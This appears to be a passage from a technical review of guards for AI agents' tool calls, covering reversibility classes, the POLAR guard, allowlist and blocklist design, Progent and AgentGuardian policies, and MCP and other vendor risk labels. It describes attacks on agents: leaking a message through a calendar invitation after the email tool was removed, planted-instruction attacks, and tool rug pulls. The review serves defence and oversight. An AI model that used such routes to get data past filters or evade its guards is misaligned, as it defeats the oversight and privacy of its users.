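The five classes did not spare users many questions either. Both the session-aware guard and the read/write rule would have asked about more than a fifth of the calls in harmless runs. Only 119 of the 770 harmless runs in which the agent originally succeeded would have finished without a question from the session-aware guard. Saving copies of private files first would have removed only one question from the harmless runs. A replay also cannot show what the agent or the user would have done after a question, so the 29 stopped calls cannot be counted as prevented attacks.

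### Testing whether undo works

A class such as R1 is a prediction that a particular undo will succeed. Waghmare and Sufi tested several of these predictions on small examples they made for the purpose.

The work began with text files. Putting back the saved copy restored a file exactly if nobody else had touched it, but erased a colleague's work if they had since edited another paragraph. A three-way merge, which compares the saved copy, the agent's version and the current file, removed the agent's edit and kept the colleague's. When both had edited the same line, the merge left the file unchanged for a person to resolve.

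In Git, a program that records versions of files, they labelled a commit R1 because a soft reset command undoes it. The reset worked for ordinary commits, but when a commit completed a merge of two lines of work, it restored the files and lost Git's record that a merge was in progress. If a colleague had since added another commit, resetting by one commit removed the colleague's commit and left the agent's in place.

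The database tests used SQLite. Creating a table and then dropping it restored the earlier state, except that an empty internal table remained if the table had used the AUTOINCREMENT option to number its rows. If someone had added a row before the drop, that person's data was lost too. A test that only compares the states before and after would have counted this as a success, because the database matched its original state exactly.

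Even closing a browser tab had no fixed risk class. Chromium and Firefox restored unsaved text in a plain text box when the user reopened the tab, but the tested version of Safari did not. None of the three restored unsaved text in a rich-text editor.

These are small tests of selected cases, with two to four examples each, so they are weak evidence of how often undo fails in general. But they show that an R1 label needs conditions. One such condition is "nobody else has changed it since", which a guard cannot confirm before the call because the change may come later.

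### Computing reversibility with POLAR

*POLAR* (Kang, Cho and colleagues, October 2026) describes a guard that searches for a sequence of calls that would undo the proposed one, and refuses the call if it finds none that is good enough. A person first describes how to undo the effects of each tool that changes data, using five relations. Each description has a weight *w*, above 0 and up to 1, that expresses that person's confidence in it.

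| Relation | Meaning | Score |
|---|---|---|
| T1, inverse | Another call exactly undoes this one | *w* |
| T2, bounded reversibility | The tool can reverse its own change while a stated condition holds | *w* if the condition holds, otherwise 0 |
| T3, compensation | Another call undoes it at a loss, such as a fee | *w* × (1 − loss) |
| T4, irreversible consumption | The call uses up something irreplaceable | 0 |
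| T5, external side effect | The call reaches the outside world, for example by email | 0 |

Before each call that would change data, POLAR rebuilds the current state from the database and the calls already made. It looks up the possible undo steps, checks their conditions against that state and scores each step. The score of a whole sequence is that of its weakest step:

```
score(sequence) = lowest score of any step in it
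```

POLAR allows the call if the score is at least 0.80. Suppose cancelling a booking undoes a purchase with a weight of 0.9 and a loss of 0.1. The score is 0.9 × (1 − 0.1) = 0.81, so the purchase goes ahead. With a loss of 0.2, the score would be 0.72, and POLAR would refuse. If the agent also tried to email a voucher, the lowest score would be 0, however easy the purchase was to cancel.

Kang and colleagues tested POLAR with six agent models on the three τ²-bench domains, with 150 attempted runs for each combination of model, domain and guard. They measured task reward, roughly the share of tasks an agent completes correctly. Reward rose in only eight of the 18 combinations of model and domain. On airline tasks, POLAR raised the reward of the four weaker models by 0.11 to 0.18, with Qwen3-8B going from 0.351 to 0.462, but lowered the strongest model's reward from 0.660 to 0.541. On shop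 tasks, it lowered gpt-oss-120B's reward from 0.455 to 0.213.

Even the airline gains may have little to do with the search. Kang and colleagues reran the airline test for Qwen3-8B with only the exact-inverse relation switched on. No airline tool has an exact inverse, since booking again after a cancellation creates a new reservation number, so this version refused nearly every change. It still raised reward by 0.087, compared with 0.080 for the full system. An agent that often books the wrong flight may do better when a guard stops it from booking.

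The log of 1,745 refusals helps explain the losses. POLAR found no complete undo sequence in 910 cases and an external side effect in 833. The calls it refused most often included returns and exchanges of delivered goods, which shop customers have good reason to request. Kang and colleagues did not label the refused calls as harmful or harmless, so nobody can calculate a miss rate or a false-block rate from their results.

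Both POLAR and the Reversibility Classes depend on what a person has written about each tool. With the Reversibility Classes, the person declares the tool's class and the guard looks it up. With POLAR, the person lists which calls undo which, and the guard works out whether a call can be undone in the current state. POLAR can therefore detect when an undo condition no longer holds, and it can show a reviewer the steps it would take. It does not run those steps to check that they work, so a wrong entry would lead to a wrong result just as a wrong label would.

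The computed score was also coarser than it looks. Across 979 approved sequences it took only four values (1.000, 0.990, 0.855 and 0.810), each corresponding to a type of relation. For an undescribed service, POLAR finds no undo and refuses every change, much as the other scheme falls back on R4. A guard for unfamiliar services therefore gains little from the search until someone has studied the tools, and by then a declared class with good argument rules is easier to write. POLAR makes more sense for a small set of well-understood tools whose state changes often.

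### Six calls and five classes

The table applies the Reversibility Classes to two simplified calls for each of three tools. Waghmare and Sufi tested similar file edits and table creation, and the classes for file sharing follow from their definitions.

| Call | Class | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| `edit_file("notes.txt", ..., dryRun=true)` | R0 | Shows the proposed edit and leaves the file alone |
| `edit_file("notes.txt", ..., dryRun=false)` | R1 | A confirmed copy of this private file exists; without one, R4 |
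| `create_table("CREATE TABLE t (id INTEGER)")` | R1 | Dropping the new table restores the earlier state |
| `create_table("CREATE TABLE t (id INTEGER PRIMARY KEY AUTOINCREMENT)")` | R2 | Dropping it leaves an empty internal table |
| `share_file("plan.pdf", "ana@ourfirm.example")` | R3 | Changes a trusted colleague's access rights |
| `share_file("plan.pdf", "sam@elsewhere.example")` | R4 | Discloses the file to an outsider |

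Every tool appears in two classes, so a single label per tool would be wrong for at least one call in each pair. The registry gives `create_table` a base class of R2, which is sensible for a guard that does not read the SQL. Younesi likewise assigns risk to the tool together with its arguments, but his tiers R0 to R3 have different meanings from the classes of the same name here.

The guard has to identify which arguments matter. *Intent-Conditioned Argument Mediation for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (2026) calls an argument "authority-bearing" if changing it can change whom or what the call affects. An email's recipient and attachment qualify, but its subject line does not. The researchers labelled these arguments by hand for their main experiments. When they tried to infer the labels for 150 arguments from six outside services, they missed 25.9% of the authority-bearing ones. With an unfamiliar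 tool, a guard will probably miss some of the arguments that determine a call's class.

Owiredu-Ashley found an attack that leaked a message through an argument of a calendar call. A filter had removed the agent's `send_email` tool, so the agent added the attacker's address to a calendar event and put the message in the invitation. The benchmark checked only for a sent email, so it counted the defence as successful. A guard that treated `create_calendar_event` as a harmless private change would also have missed the disclosure, because the `participants` argument made the event a disclosure.

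A call's arguments still do not always determine its risk class. Railway's new 48-hour delay may put the PocketOS request in a lower class, even though its arguments have not changed. The class assigned to a call to an outside service should therefore have a date and a stated reason, so that someone can check whether it still holds.

### Where reasonable raters differ

Many calls, such as opening a GitHub issue or moving a meeting, notify people as a by-product. Waghmare and Sufi put a call in R4 if its purpose is to deliver content to outsiders. If the notification is incidental, they ignore it and judge the call only by whether the agent can undo the change. A stricter rater would put both kinds of call in R4, because nobody can recall the email in either case. Waghmare and Sufi acknowledge that the boundary needs clearer guidance.

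Under the strict reading, most shared calendars, documents and task lists would end up in R4 because so many services send notifications, and the guard would ask about nearly every change. But purpose is a poor test because the guard cannot see what the agent intended. If an agent pastes a password into a public GitHub issue, the project's followers may receive it by email whether or not anyone meant to send it.

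A better test is what the notification contains and who receives it. An automatic "this meeting has moved" message to colleagues reveals little, so the guard can classify the call by whether the agent can move the meeting back. A notification that copies the agent's text to outsiders is a disclosure and belongs in R4. For this test, the guard needs a list of insiders and some information about what each service puts in its notifications. If it has neither, the cautious choice is to assume that outsiders will receive the full text.

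Raters also disagree about who may carry out a recovery and whether to count possible failures. The registry puts closing a browser in R3, while Sufi's review put it in R4. Either rating can be right, depending on whether the page contains a half-written draft and whether the browser saves it.

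## Writing and maintaining an allowlist

Assigning a good risk class requires someone who has studied the tool. An allowlist records the calls that such a person has already judged acceptable, so the guard only has to recognise them.

### How a call matches an entry

The guard compares each call with the list in five steps:

1. It normalises the call, which means putting it into a standard form. It decodes the address, parses the body and splits a chain of commands into single commands.
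2. It finds the entries for the service, which it identifies by host, program or MCP server.
3. It compares the operation, such as a GraphQL field or a subcommand.
4. It checks the arguments against the limits in the entry.
5. If everything matches, it allows the call. Otherwise it passes the call on to the next check.

A call that matches no allowlist entry has unknown risk. Most such calls may be harmless, so another check or a person has to judge them.

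Good normalising lets harmless variations of a command match. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, strips certain prefixes before matching, so an entry for `npm test` also covers `timeout 30 npm test`, which stops the test after 30 seconds. According to Anthropic's documentation, a chain of commands runs without a question only if every command in it qualifies. Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, splits only simple chains. According to OpenAI's *Rules*, Codex treats a script with variables, redirections or loops as one command that starts with the name of the shell, the program that runs typed commands, so an entry for a command inside the script doesn't match. This causes some needless questions, but the guard never approves a script just because a command in it is on the allowlist.

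### Exact entries, wildcards and argument limits

| Form | Example | What it allows | Usual problem |
|---|---|---|---|
| Exact | `git status` | That command only | Harmless variations don't match |
| Wildcard | `git branch *` | Any arguments, including `-D old`, which deletes a branch | The entry covers more than its author had in mind |
| Argument limits | `send_money` to the landlord, up to 900 euros | Any payment within the limits, including a second one | The author has to know what each argument does |

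The wildcard problem is easy to overlook. A sample pattern in the documentation for Zed, a code editor, allows `git status`, `git log`, `git diff` and `git branch` with anything after them. By itself, `git branch` lists a project's branches (its parallel lines of work), so it seems to belong with the others.

*ToolFence* (2026) uses a `send_money` tool to show why an allowlist should check more than a tool's name. If the list contains only the name, the model can send money to any recipient. Checking one argument isn't enough either, because one acceptable value doesn't make the whole call safe. For this reason, Claude Code lets a rule match a single parameter if the rule blocks calls or requires the user's approval, but not if it allows them.

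Limits on arguments work best when the arguments are in separate, named fields, as they are in an MCP call. In a command line they are part of a string, and Anthropic calls patterns meant to constrain them "fragile". VS Code's *Manage approvals and permissions* describes automatic approval of terminal commands as a convenience and "not a security boundary", partly because the editor's parser may not find every command in a line.

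### An entry for a GraphQL service

This entry, in an invented format, allows the harmless Railway request mentioned earlier, which fetches the user's own name and email:

```
service:         POST https://backboard.railway.app/graphql/v2
operation:       exactly one, of type query
fields:          me { name email }
arguments:       none
reason:          reads the account holder's own details
reviewed:        2026-12-01
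expires:         2027-03-01
must match:      query { me { name email } }
                 { me { email } }
must not match:  { me { name workspaces { id } } }
                 mutation { volumeDelete(volumeId: "...") }
```

The guard has to parse the request, because searching for the word "query" would give wrong answers. Under the GraphQL specification, a client can leave the word out of a simple query, as in the second example. A document can also contain several operations, with the client naming the one to run, so the entry accepts only documents with a single operation. Clients can also rename fields in the response, so the guard should compare the original names.

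Some GraphQL servers run only operations stored in advance. The GraphQL Foundation's *Security* calls these "trusted documents", and the server usually identifies each one by a hash, a short fingerprint computed from its text. A public API's provider can't use this method for outside customers, because it doesn't know what they will send. A guard could keep a similar list for one agent, but an agent that writes new queries each time would seldom repeat one exactly.

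### An entry for a command-line tool

The next entry uses Codex's format and is adapted from an example in OpenAI's documentation. The original example has Codex ask the user before running the command, but this entry allows it without asking.

```
prefix_rule(
    pattern = ["gh", "pr", "view"],
    decision = "allow",
    justification = "Shows a proposed code change, edits nothing",
    match = ["gh pr view 7888"],
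    not_match = ["gh pr merge 7888"],
)
```

The pattern fixes the first three words of the command. Codex tests the `match` and `not_match` examples when it loads the file, so it could catch a typo that made the pattern too broad before the entry takes effect. The agent can still add any words after the prefix, including the `--repo` option, which selects another project. The entry therefore lets the agent read proposed changes in every private project that the user's login can reach. Preventing this would require a guard that can limit the value of `--repo`.

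### Why an entry should describe what it allows

An allowlist entry for database commands is safer when it specifies what it permits, such as SELECT on named columns of the `orders` table, without function calls. A command that calls an unfamiliar function would then go to the next check. A rule such as "allow any database command that doesn't contain DELETE or DROP" takes less work to write, but it would allow `SELECT archive_customer(42)`, whatever the function does, and every other operation that the rule's author didn't think to exclude.

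A blocklist, which names the calls to stop and allows the rest, has the same weakness. GitHub gives this example for its Copilot agent:

```
copilot --allow-all-tools --deny-tool='shell(rm)' --deny-tool='shell(git push)'
```

These settings would have allowed the PocketOS deletion, which the agent sent with `curl`. Leaving a safe operation off an allowlist leads to an unnecessary question, while leaving a dangerous one off a blocklist may let it run unchecked. If the service is unfamiliar, the author doesn't know which operations to block.

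A blocklist is still useful alongside an allowlist for firm prohibitions. Claude Code applies block, ask and allow rules in that order, so a specific permission can't override a general ban. Block and allow rules also need different matching. In *Decision Models as Policy Gates for Coding Agents* (2026), a block or ask rule matches if any part of the call is hazardous, while an allow rule matches only if the whole call is within its scope.

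### Benefits and coverage

An allowlist always gives the same result for the same call, whatever the agent has read or been told. A team can keep it under version control, see who added an entry and why, and test it before use. Checking a call against it takes almost no time and requires no model. In Claude Code's auto mode, a learned classifier replaces the user's approval, but Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that allow rules clear most actions before they reach the classifier.

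The main cost is the work of covering operations that the agent rarely uses. Suppose a company's agents use 400 different operations, and the second most common gets half as many calls as the first, the third gets a third as many, and so on. If the author adds entries in order of use, the share of calls covered by *k* entries is

```
coverage(k) = (1 + 1/2 + ... + 1/k) ÷ (1 + 1/2 + ... + 1/400)
```

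| Entries | Calls covered | Review time at 10 minutes each |
|---|---|---|
| 10 | 45% | 1.7 hours |
| 50 | 68% | 8 hours |
| 100 | 79% | 17 hours |
| 200 | 89% | 33 hours |

The second hundred entries take as long to review as the first but add only ten percentage points of coverage. Even with 200 entries, a 20-call task would have only about an 11% chance of finishing without an unmatched call if the calls were independent. Real tasks tend to repeat the same few operations, so the true chance is probably higher. But some of the 400 operations will be payments or deletions, and no entry should allow every call to those. Some suppliers publish catalogues of read-only operations, which can save part of the work.

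*Stop asking me* (2026), a blog post by a Claude Code user, describes writing more than 80 narrow allowlist patterns and spending a week adjusting them. Permission prompts kept appearing, often for chains of several commands, and the user then replaced the patterns with one broad permission. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025) notes that a developer or administrator can write the access rules for ordinary software, but an agent may have only a user, who may know little about security.

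### The rules that users write

In June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written an allow rule for shell commands, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). The post adds that 5% allowed any shell command and another 43% had rules such as `Bash(python:*)`, which allows every command that starts Python. The post does not make clear whether the last two figures are shares of all active users, in which case nearly everyone who wrote a rule wrote an almost unlimited one, or only of those who had written a rule, in which case about half did. Anthropic put the growth at roughly five percentage points every five weeks.

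Python is an interpreter that runs whatever code it is given, so a match on an allowlist rule for `python` gives the guard no evidence about the call's effect. The command `python report.py` may add up a column of numbers or delete a database, depending on the file's contents.

Anthropic published these figures to promote auto mode, which disables overly broad allowlist rules because they would let commands skip the classifier. Narrow rules, such as permission to run a code formatter, still apply. The company admits that its list of overly broad rules is bound to be incomplete. One customer, Garner Health, made auto mode the default for all 550 employees and no longer relies on hand-compiled command allowlists.

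### Policies that a model writes

If people write rules that are too broad, a language model might write narrower ones for each task. Shi, He and colleagues (2025) built such a guard in *Progent*. Before the agent reads any outside data, a model writes rules for tool names and arguments based on the user's request and the available tools. The guard blocks every call that no rule allows.

An agent often learns what it needs only as it works. In one of the researchers' examples, a user asks it to carry out a to-do list in an email, and the list tells it to post a summary on the chat service Slack. The model can therefore propose a new policy after each result. A solver, a program that settles logical questions exactly, compares the two policies. If *A*(*P*) is the set of calls that policy *P* allows, the new policy takes effect automatically only when

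```
A(new) ⊆ A(old)
```

This condition means the new policy allows nothing that the old one blocked. Restricting Slack messages to the recipient `alice` meets the condition, so the guard applies the change immediately. Adding `send_email` does not meet it, so that change needs approval.

Shi and colleagues tested Progent with GPT-4o on two sets of planted-instruction attacks. On AgentDojo, 39.9% of the attacks succeeded without Progent and 1.0% with it. On Agent Security Bench, 70.3% succeeded without it and 3.9% with it. The agent completed about as many tasks with Progent as without it. These results assume a careless user who approves every expansion of the policy. On AgentDojo, the first policy without updates cut attack success to 2.5%, and no attacks succeeded when a person reviewed the first policy and every expansion. Only 6% of the updates were expansions. A simpler defence that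 selected whole tools by name stopped fewer attacks and let the agent complete fewer tasks.

*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that malicious text in a tool's result may lead Progent to relax its own rules. The solver detects when rules are relaxed but can't determine whether the change is legitimate, so the protection depends on whoever approves the change. The published figures also don't include a false-block rate for individual calls. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) recommends that researchers measure wrongful refusals and the burden on users as well as the attacks stopped.

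A more basic limit for unfamiliar services is that Progent relies on tools' names and descriptions to estimate which calls a task needs. Most of its failures on Agent Security Bench involved attack tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate ones. Its rules are better evidence that the user wants a call than of what the call will do.

### Policies learned from past calls

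Allowlist entries can also come from logs of normal work. In *AgentGuardian*, Abaev, Klimov and colleagues (2026) recorded a research assistant and an IT support agent during a trial period, assuming that every run was legitimate. Their program grouped similar calls, and a language model turned each group into text patterns for the arguments. The policy also limited things like running time and the order in which the agent could use its tools.

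The researchers built the policies from 60 runs of each application and tested them on 80 legitimate and 20 improper runs in total. The guard missed two of the improper runs (10%) and wrongly rejected eight of the legitimate ones (10%). With only 20 improper runs, the true miss rate could plausibly be between about 1% and 32%. Half of the wrongful rejections involved unusually long inputs or running times, and the others departed from the recorded order of steps.

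Small samples produced poor policies. With ten runs, the pattern for a file-writing tool matched practically any text. Even the published example of a finished policy is looser than its description. It is supposed to limit an agent to certain text files in two folders, but the pattern is

```
\./(Cars/[^\s]*|AI/ai\-[^\s]*\-2025|[^\s]*)\.txt
```

The last alternative inside the brackets, `[^\s]*`, matches any text without spaces, so the pattern also accepts `.txt` files in other folders. One test with a path that must not match, such as `./Payroll/may.txt`, would have exposed the error. Learned entries need the same tests as handwritten ones, and a reviewer also has to check whether a frequent call is acceptable.

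### When an approved operation changes

An entry records what an operation did on the day of the review. Railway's `volumeDelete` gained a 48-hour delay under the same name, and a supplier could just as easily remove one. A supplier can also win approval for a harmless tool and then make it harmful, an attack known as a rug pull. *ETDI* (2025) gives the example of a wallpaper tool that keeps its name and version number but starts uploading the user's financial documents. According to *MCP-38* (2026), current MCP clients don't alert users when a tool's definition changes.

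The usual remedy is version pinning, which ties an allowlist entry to one release of a tool. The guard can also store a hash of the tool's description and argument list, and stop matching the entry if the hash changes. *ToolFence* keeps the reviewed definitions in a separate list that the guard's operator controls, because suppliers can write the descriptions the agent sees.

Pinning doesn't catch every change. *ProbeID* (Chen, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) repeatedly sent test calls to 59 tools on 16 published MCP servers over eleven weeks. Seven tools (12%) began to respond differently with no change in version number, three of them after a reinstallation. A pinned server can still load newer supporting software or contact a remote service that has changed, and a hash of the definition reveals neither. The 12% is only a rough guide to changes in risk, since a tool's response can change without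 its effect changing, and vice versa.

Expiry dates limit the damage from changes that nobody notices. If every entry lapses after 90 days unless someone renews it, an outdated entry stays in use for at most 90 days, or 45 on average if changes come at random times. At ten minutes per entry, renewing 200 entries would take about 33 hours each quarter. An author can reduce this work by giving longer terms to entries for pinned local programs and keeping short terms for remote services, which the supplier can change at any time. For one-off work, VS Code offers approvals that end with the session.

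Reviewers should also check whether anyone still needs the entry. *Aletheia* (2026) tests this for the permissions that a coding project's rules request. It runs a task with and without a permission and reports the permission as suspicious if the agent can finish without it. Other tasks may still need that permission, so a guard's author would have to repeat the test on a range of typical tasks before deleting the entry.

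## Using what the vendor declares

Anyone who writes an allowlist has to study every operation before approving it, and people who write other guards repeat the same work. The vendor already knows what its operations do, so it could publish a machine-readable label for each one.

Vendors are well placed to write these labels. In April 2026, Railway's staff knew that customers could not undo a volume deletion made through the API, but PocketOS learned this only when it lost its database. Labelling also takes less time overall if the vendor does it. If a service has 60 operations and each takes ten minutes to label, the vendor spends ten hours once, while 500 guard authors labelling them separately would spend 5,000 hours. The vendor also knows about a change before anyone else and can update the label in the same release. But vendors don't always do this, as Railway's outdated documentation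 showed.

### From a label to a decision

A guard can use a vendor declaration in four steps:

1. It fetches the supplier's description of the service. An MCP server, for example, returns one when the host asks which tools it offers.
2. It finds the entry for the operation in the proposed call.
3. It fills in a default value for any missing label.
4. It translates the labels into one of its own risk classes and adjusts the class if it has rules for the call's arguments.

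The translation is imprecise, as Waghmare and Sufi found when they compared such hints with their own labels.

### MCP's four hints

MCP has included labels called tool annotations since March 2025. Apart from a display title, they consist of four optional hints, each true or false:

| Hint | Default | Meaning when true | When it applies |
|---|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | false | The tool does not modify its environment | Always |
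| `destructiveHint` | true | The tool may delete or overwrite data; false means it only adds | If the tool is not read-only |
| `idempotentHint` | false | Repeating the call with the same arguments has no further effect | If the tool is not read-only |
| `openWorldHint` | true | The tool may deal with outside systems or people | Always |

Nuri's *MCP Tool Annotations* (2025, updated October 2026) takes its examples from the Kubernetes MCP Server, which lets an agent manage applications on a cluster of computers. Its tool for uninstalling an application has annotations like these, shortened here:

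```
{"name": "helm_uninstall",
 "annotations": {"readOnlyHint": false,
                 "destructiveHint": true,
                 "idempotentHint": true}}
```

A guard can infer that the call may delete something and that repeating it would do no further damage. This excerpt has no `openWorldHint`, so the guard treats that hint as true.

If a tool has no annotations, the guard applies all four defaults. It assumes that the tool can change data, may destroy some of it, is unsafe to repeat and deals with the outside world. These defaults cause many needless questions, as R4 does for unrecognised calls. Not every host follows them.

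Many combinations of hints mean the same thing. Each hint can be true, false or missing, which gives 3⁴ = 81 combinations. For a guard that follows the defaults, a missing hint means the same as its default value, so only 16 remain. If `readOnlyHint` is true, `destructiveHint` and `idempotentHint` no longer apply, so the eight read-only combinations shrink to two, leaving ten distinct meanings. Sixteen of the original 81 combinations are equivalent to no annotations, because every hint in them is either missing or set to its default.

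A guard also can't assume that a developer chose every value it receives. Nuri reports that the official MCP library for Go always sends `readOnlyHint` and `idempotentHint`, so a value of false may come from the library. In version 1 of the Python library, a developer who writes `read_only_hint` instead of `readOnlyHint` gets no error, but hosts don't recognise the hint.

### Accurate hints that mislead

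A guard can misjudge a call even when the hints are accurate, if it infers more from them than they mean. MCP distinguishes "destructive" changes from additive ones, which is not the same as distinguishing irreversible changes from reversible ones. Sending an email adds a message and deletes nothing, so a developer could reasonably set `destructiveHint` to false. A guard that asked for approval only for tools marked destructive would then let the agent email a customer list to a stranger. Overwriting a file is destructive in MCP's sense, but the agent can undo it if it has access to an earlier version.

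The read-only hint doesn't rule out disclosure either. AgentDojo's `get_webpage` can leak data through the URL it requests, and it would still be accurately labeled read-only and open-world. A guard should therefore not automatically allow a read-only tool that is also open-world.

The open-world hint is ambiguous. According to a March 2026 post on the Model Context Protocol blog, "external" might mean anything outside a company's network or anything beyond the local machine. Nuri marks tools that contact a Kubernetes cluster as open-world, but under OpenAI's rules for plugins, as Nuri reports them, a private workspace isn't open-world merely because another company hosts it.

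The hints also apply to a whole tool, so a tool such as `edit_file`, which can either preview an edit or make it, can't accurately be marked read-only. The guard will therefore ask about previews too. Nuri advises developers to split such a tool in two.

### Labels outside MCP

Amazon Web Services (AWS), Amazon's cloud computing business, labels the actions in its own services. An action here is a permission that AWS checks when someone performs an operation. AWS's *Access levels in policy summaries* defines five levels:

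- List: find out which resources exist without seeing their contents.
- Read: see the contents and attributes of resources.
- Tagging: change only the tags on a resource.
- Write: create, delete or modify resources.
- Permissions management: control who has access.

The separate level for permissions is useful because none of MCP's hints identifies a call that gives someone lasting access. However, it excludes network controls, so changing a server's firewall rules doesn't count as permissions management. The write level is so broad that a guard relying on it would treat creating a storage bucket and deleting one alike. Fetching a database password and fetching a public logo are both reads by AWS's definition.

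AWS also publishes the labels as files that a program can download. Each action has four true-or-false properties, `IsList`, `IsWrite`, `IsTaggingOnly` and `IsPermissionManagement`, and more than one can be true. If all four are false, the action only reads. A guard that fills in false for missing values would therefore treat every unlabelled action as a read. The guard must also work out which actions a call uses. The entry for the storage operation `GetObject` lists six actions, and for some services AWS doesn't publish this mapping.

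OpenAI's label has only two values. A GPT action connects a customised version of ChatGPT to an outside API, which the builder describes in OpenAPI, a common format for listing an API's operations. The builder can add the field `x-openai-isConsequential` to an operation. According to OpenAI's *Production notes on GPT Actions*, ChatGPT then behaves as follows:

| Value | What ChatGPT does |
|---|---|
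| true | Always asks before running the operation |
| false | Offers an "always allow" button |
| missing | Treats GET as false and every other method as true |

The default has the same weaknesses as any rule based on HTTP methods. It would offer "always allow" for a GET request that sends a Telegram message, and ask every time about an Elasticsearch search sent by POST. A builder who knows the services can correct each with one line. Microsoft uses a similar default for Microsoft 365 Copilot, which normally offers "always allow" only for GET. The person who writes OpenAI's flag may have no connection with the service, and the flag then lacks the main advantage of a vendor declaration.

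Developers who use gRPC, a system for calling functions on another computer, usually describe their services in a language called Protobuf. They can mark each method as having no side effects or as idempotent, and an unmarked method counts as unknown:

```
rpc GetBalance(BalanceRequest) returns (Balance) {
  option idempotency_level = NO_SIDE_EFFECTS;
}
```

Connect, a related system that also works over ordinary HTTP, uses this marker to determine which methods clients can call with GET. Connect's *Get Requests and Caching* explains that clients can send a marked method as a GET request, while all other methods use POST. A GET request to a Connect service is therefore evidence that a developer marked the method as free of side effects, even if the guard has never seen the service's description. However, the marker does not prevent the method's code from changing data.

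Smithy, a language from Amazon for describing services, has the similar markers `readonly` and `idempotent`. It can also identify the field that holds an idempotency key:

```
structure PayInvoiceInput {
    invoiceId: String
    @idempotencyToken
    clientToken: String
}
```

Smithy's *Behavior traits* requires a service that receives such a key to discard repeated requests for a period that the service chooses. A guard that sees two payments with the same `clientToken` can therefore treat the second as a retry until that period ends. The caller's software may fill in the key automatically.

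Some vendors may want to describe risks that these formats don't cover. *Design Considerations and Profile for HTTP APIs Consumed by AI Agents* (Gaikwad, 2026) recommends stating an operation's side effects in its description rather than leaving clients to infer them from the HTTP method. It also recommends marking high-risk operations with explicit metadata, such as a flag that the operation cannot be undone. The document is an individual Internet-Draft, a working document that anyone can submit to the IETF, and it expires on 1 January 2027. It defines no standard names for the flags, so one vendor might write `irreversible` and another `needs_confirmation`, and a guard's author would have to look up both.

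Gaikwad also suggests a declaration for a single call. In one of the draft's examples, an agent asks what would happen if it archived a project, and the service answers without archiving it. The answer, shortened here, is more specific than any fixed label:

```
"would_change": {"tasks_closed": 14, "members_notified": 6},
"reversible": true
```

A guard could use this answer to estimate how many people the call affects. But it shouldn't rely on the word `reversible`, because the agent can reopen the project but can't recall six notifications.

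API Changelog's *The Taxonomy of API Operations* proposes adding an `x-taxonomy` field to OpenAPI documents, with eight categories including bulk, workflow and simulated. Its example of a hidden effect is `POST /orders`, which might only record an order or start a chain of events that ends with a delivery. The article warns that labels will go out of date as an API changes.

| Scheme | Who writes the label | What one label covers | What enforces it |
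|---|---|---|---|
| MCP annotations | Developer of the MCP server | One tool | Nothing in the protocol |
| AWS access levels | AWS | One action | AWS checks permission for the action, but not the label |
| OpenAI's flag | Builder of the GPT | One operation | ChatGPT asks the user, but nothing makes the flag accurate |
| Protobuf marker | API developer | One method | Nothing makes the code match; Connect limits GET to marked methods |
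| Smithy traits | API developer | One operation or input field | The service has to discard repeated keys itself |
| Gaikwad's draft | API supplier | One operation, or one call in a preview | Nothing |

### The dispute over untrusted hints

MCP's developers debated the value of annotations before adopting them. Justin Spahr-Summers, one of the protocol's creators, thought the information would be very useful if clients could trust it, but wondered how a client would use a flag "knowing that it's not trustable". Basil Hosmer went further, arguing that clients should ignore every annotation from an untrusted server, even the display title.

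They settled on a compromise, according to the post on the Model Context Protocol blog. Every annotation is a hint, clients must treat hints as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server, and each client decides how much weight to give them. The documentation for the official C# library is stricter. According to Model Context Protocol's *Class ToolAnnotations*, clients should never base decisions about using a tool on annotations from untrusted servers.

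A dishonest supplier gains by understating a risk and has little reason to overstate it, so a guard can let an untrusted hint raise a call's risk class but never lower it. This partly answers Spahr-Summers's question. In practice, it differs little from Hosmer's rule, because a guard that follows the defaults already assumes the worst. A warning changes the guard's decision only if other evidence had made the call look safe. For example, the name `get_report` suggests a safe call, but the tool's `destructiveHint` might be true.

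Trusted servers are the harder case, because their hints can lead a host to skip asking the user for approval. Most of the hosts Nuri checked in October 2026 let read-only tools run without asking, at least in some modes. The blog post reports that most clients treat installation as the sign of trust. Installation is weak evidence that a tool's labels are correct, because someone who installs a calendar tool has probably not checked them, and an honest developer can still get one wrong. Anthropic's connector directory and OpenAI's plugin review now require annotations, and Nuri writes that such directories reject servers whose annotations don't match their tools. This gives developers a reason to label carefully, though only testing can show whether a tool behaves as labeled.

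### Hints and contracts

The blog post distinguishes hints, which inform a decision, from contracts, which are enforced. An annotation that is useful only when it is true needs to be a contract, so it should go where software can enforce it, such as in the system that grants permissions.

A developer can enforce a label in the server itself, as the Kubernetes MCP Server does. If an administrator turns on its read-only mode, the server stops offering any tool that lacks a true `readOnlyHint`. Nuri tested this with three groups of tools enabled. The server offered 23 tools normally, 17 with a setting that hides destructive tools, and 15 in read-only mode. In this mode, an agent can't call the missing tools through this server, even if the host ignores the hints.

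Read-only mode still depends on correct labels, and it applies only to this one server. The server's `configuration_view` tool is correctly labelled as read-only but returns the cluster's login credentials. An agent that can also run shell commands could use them to make changes directly. Nuri therefore recommends leaving out the group that contains this tool and giving the server a login with only the permissions the agent needs.

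### Proposals for new annotations

The current MCP specification, dated 28 July 2026, has the same four hints and defaults as the March 2025 version. Developers have proposed many additions, but Nuri reported that the project had accepted none of them as of late October.

In March 2026, five proposals were open. Three would each add a single hint: `secretHint`, `unsafeOutputHint` and `trustedHint`. The other two were broader. One covered governance and the user interface, and the other, SEP-1913, covered trust and sensitive data. GitHub and OpenAI staff wrote SEP-1913 after finding gaps while running MCP in their own products. It was still a draft in October.

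Willison uses the term "lethal trifecta" for the combination of access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to send data out. An agent with all three can follow a malicious instruction on a web page and send the user's files to whoever wrote it. The existing hints can suggest that a tool deals with outsiders, but none of them identifies a tool that reads private data, so a guard can't recognise the combination from the hints alone.

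A Tool Annotations Interest Group, whose two facilitators work at GitHub and OpenAI, is reviewing the proposals. Under its April 2026 charter on the Model Context Protocol site, the group can make recommendations but can't change the specification. It is also considering whether annotations should be allowed to change between calls, which might help with tools whose effect depends on their arguments.

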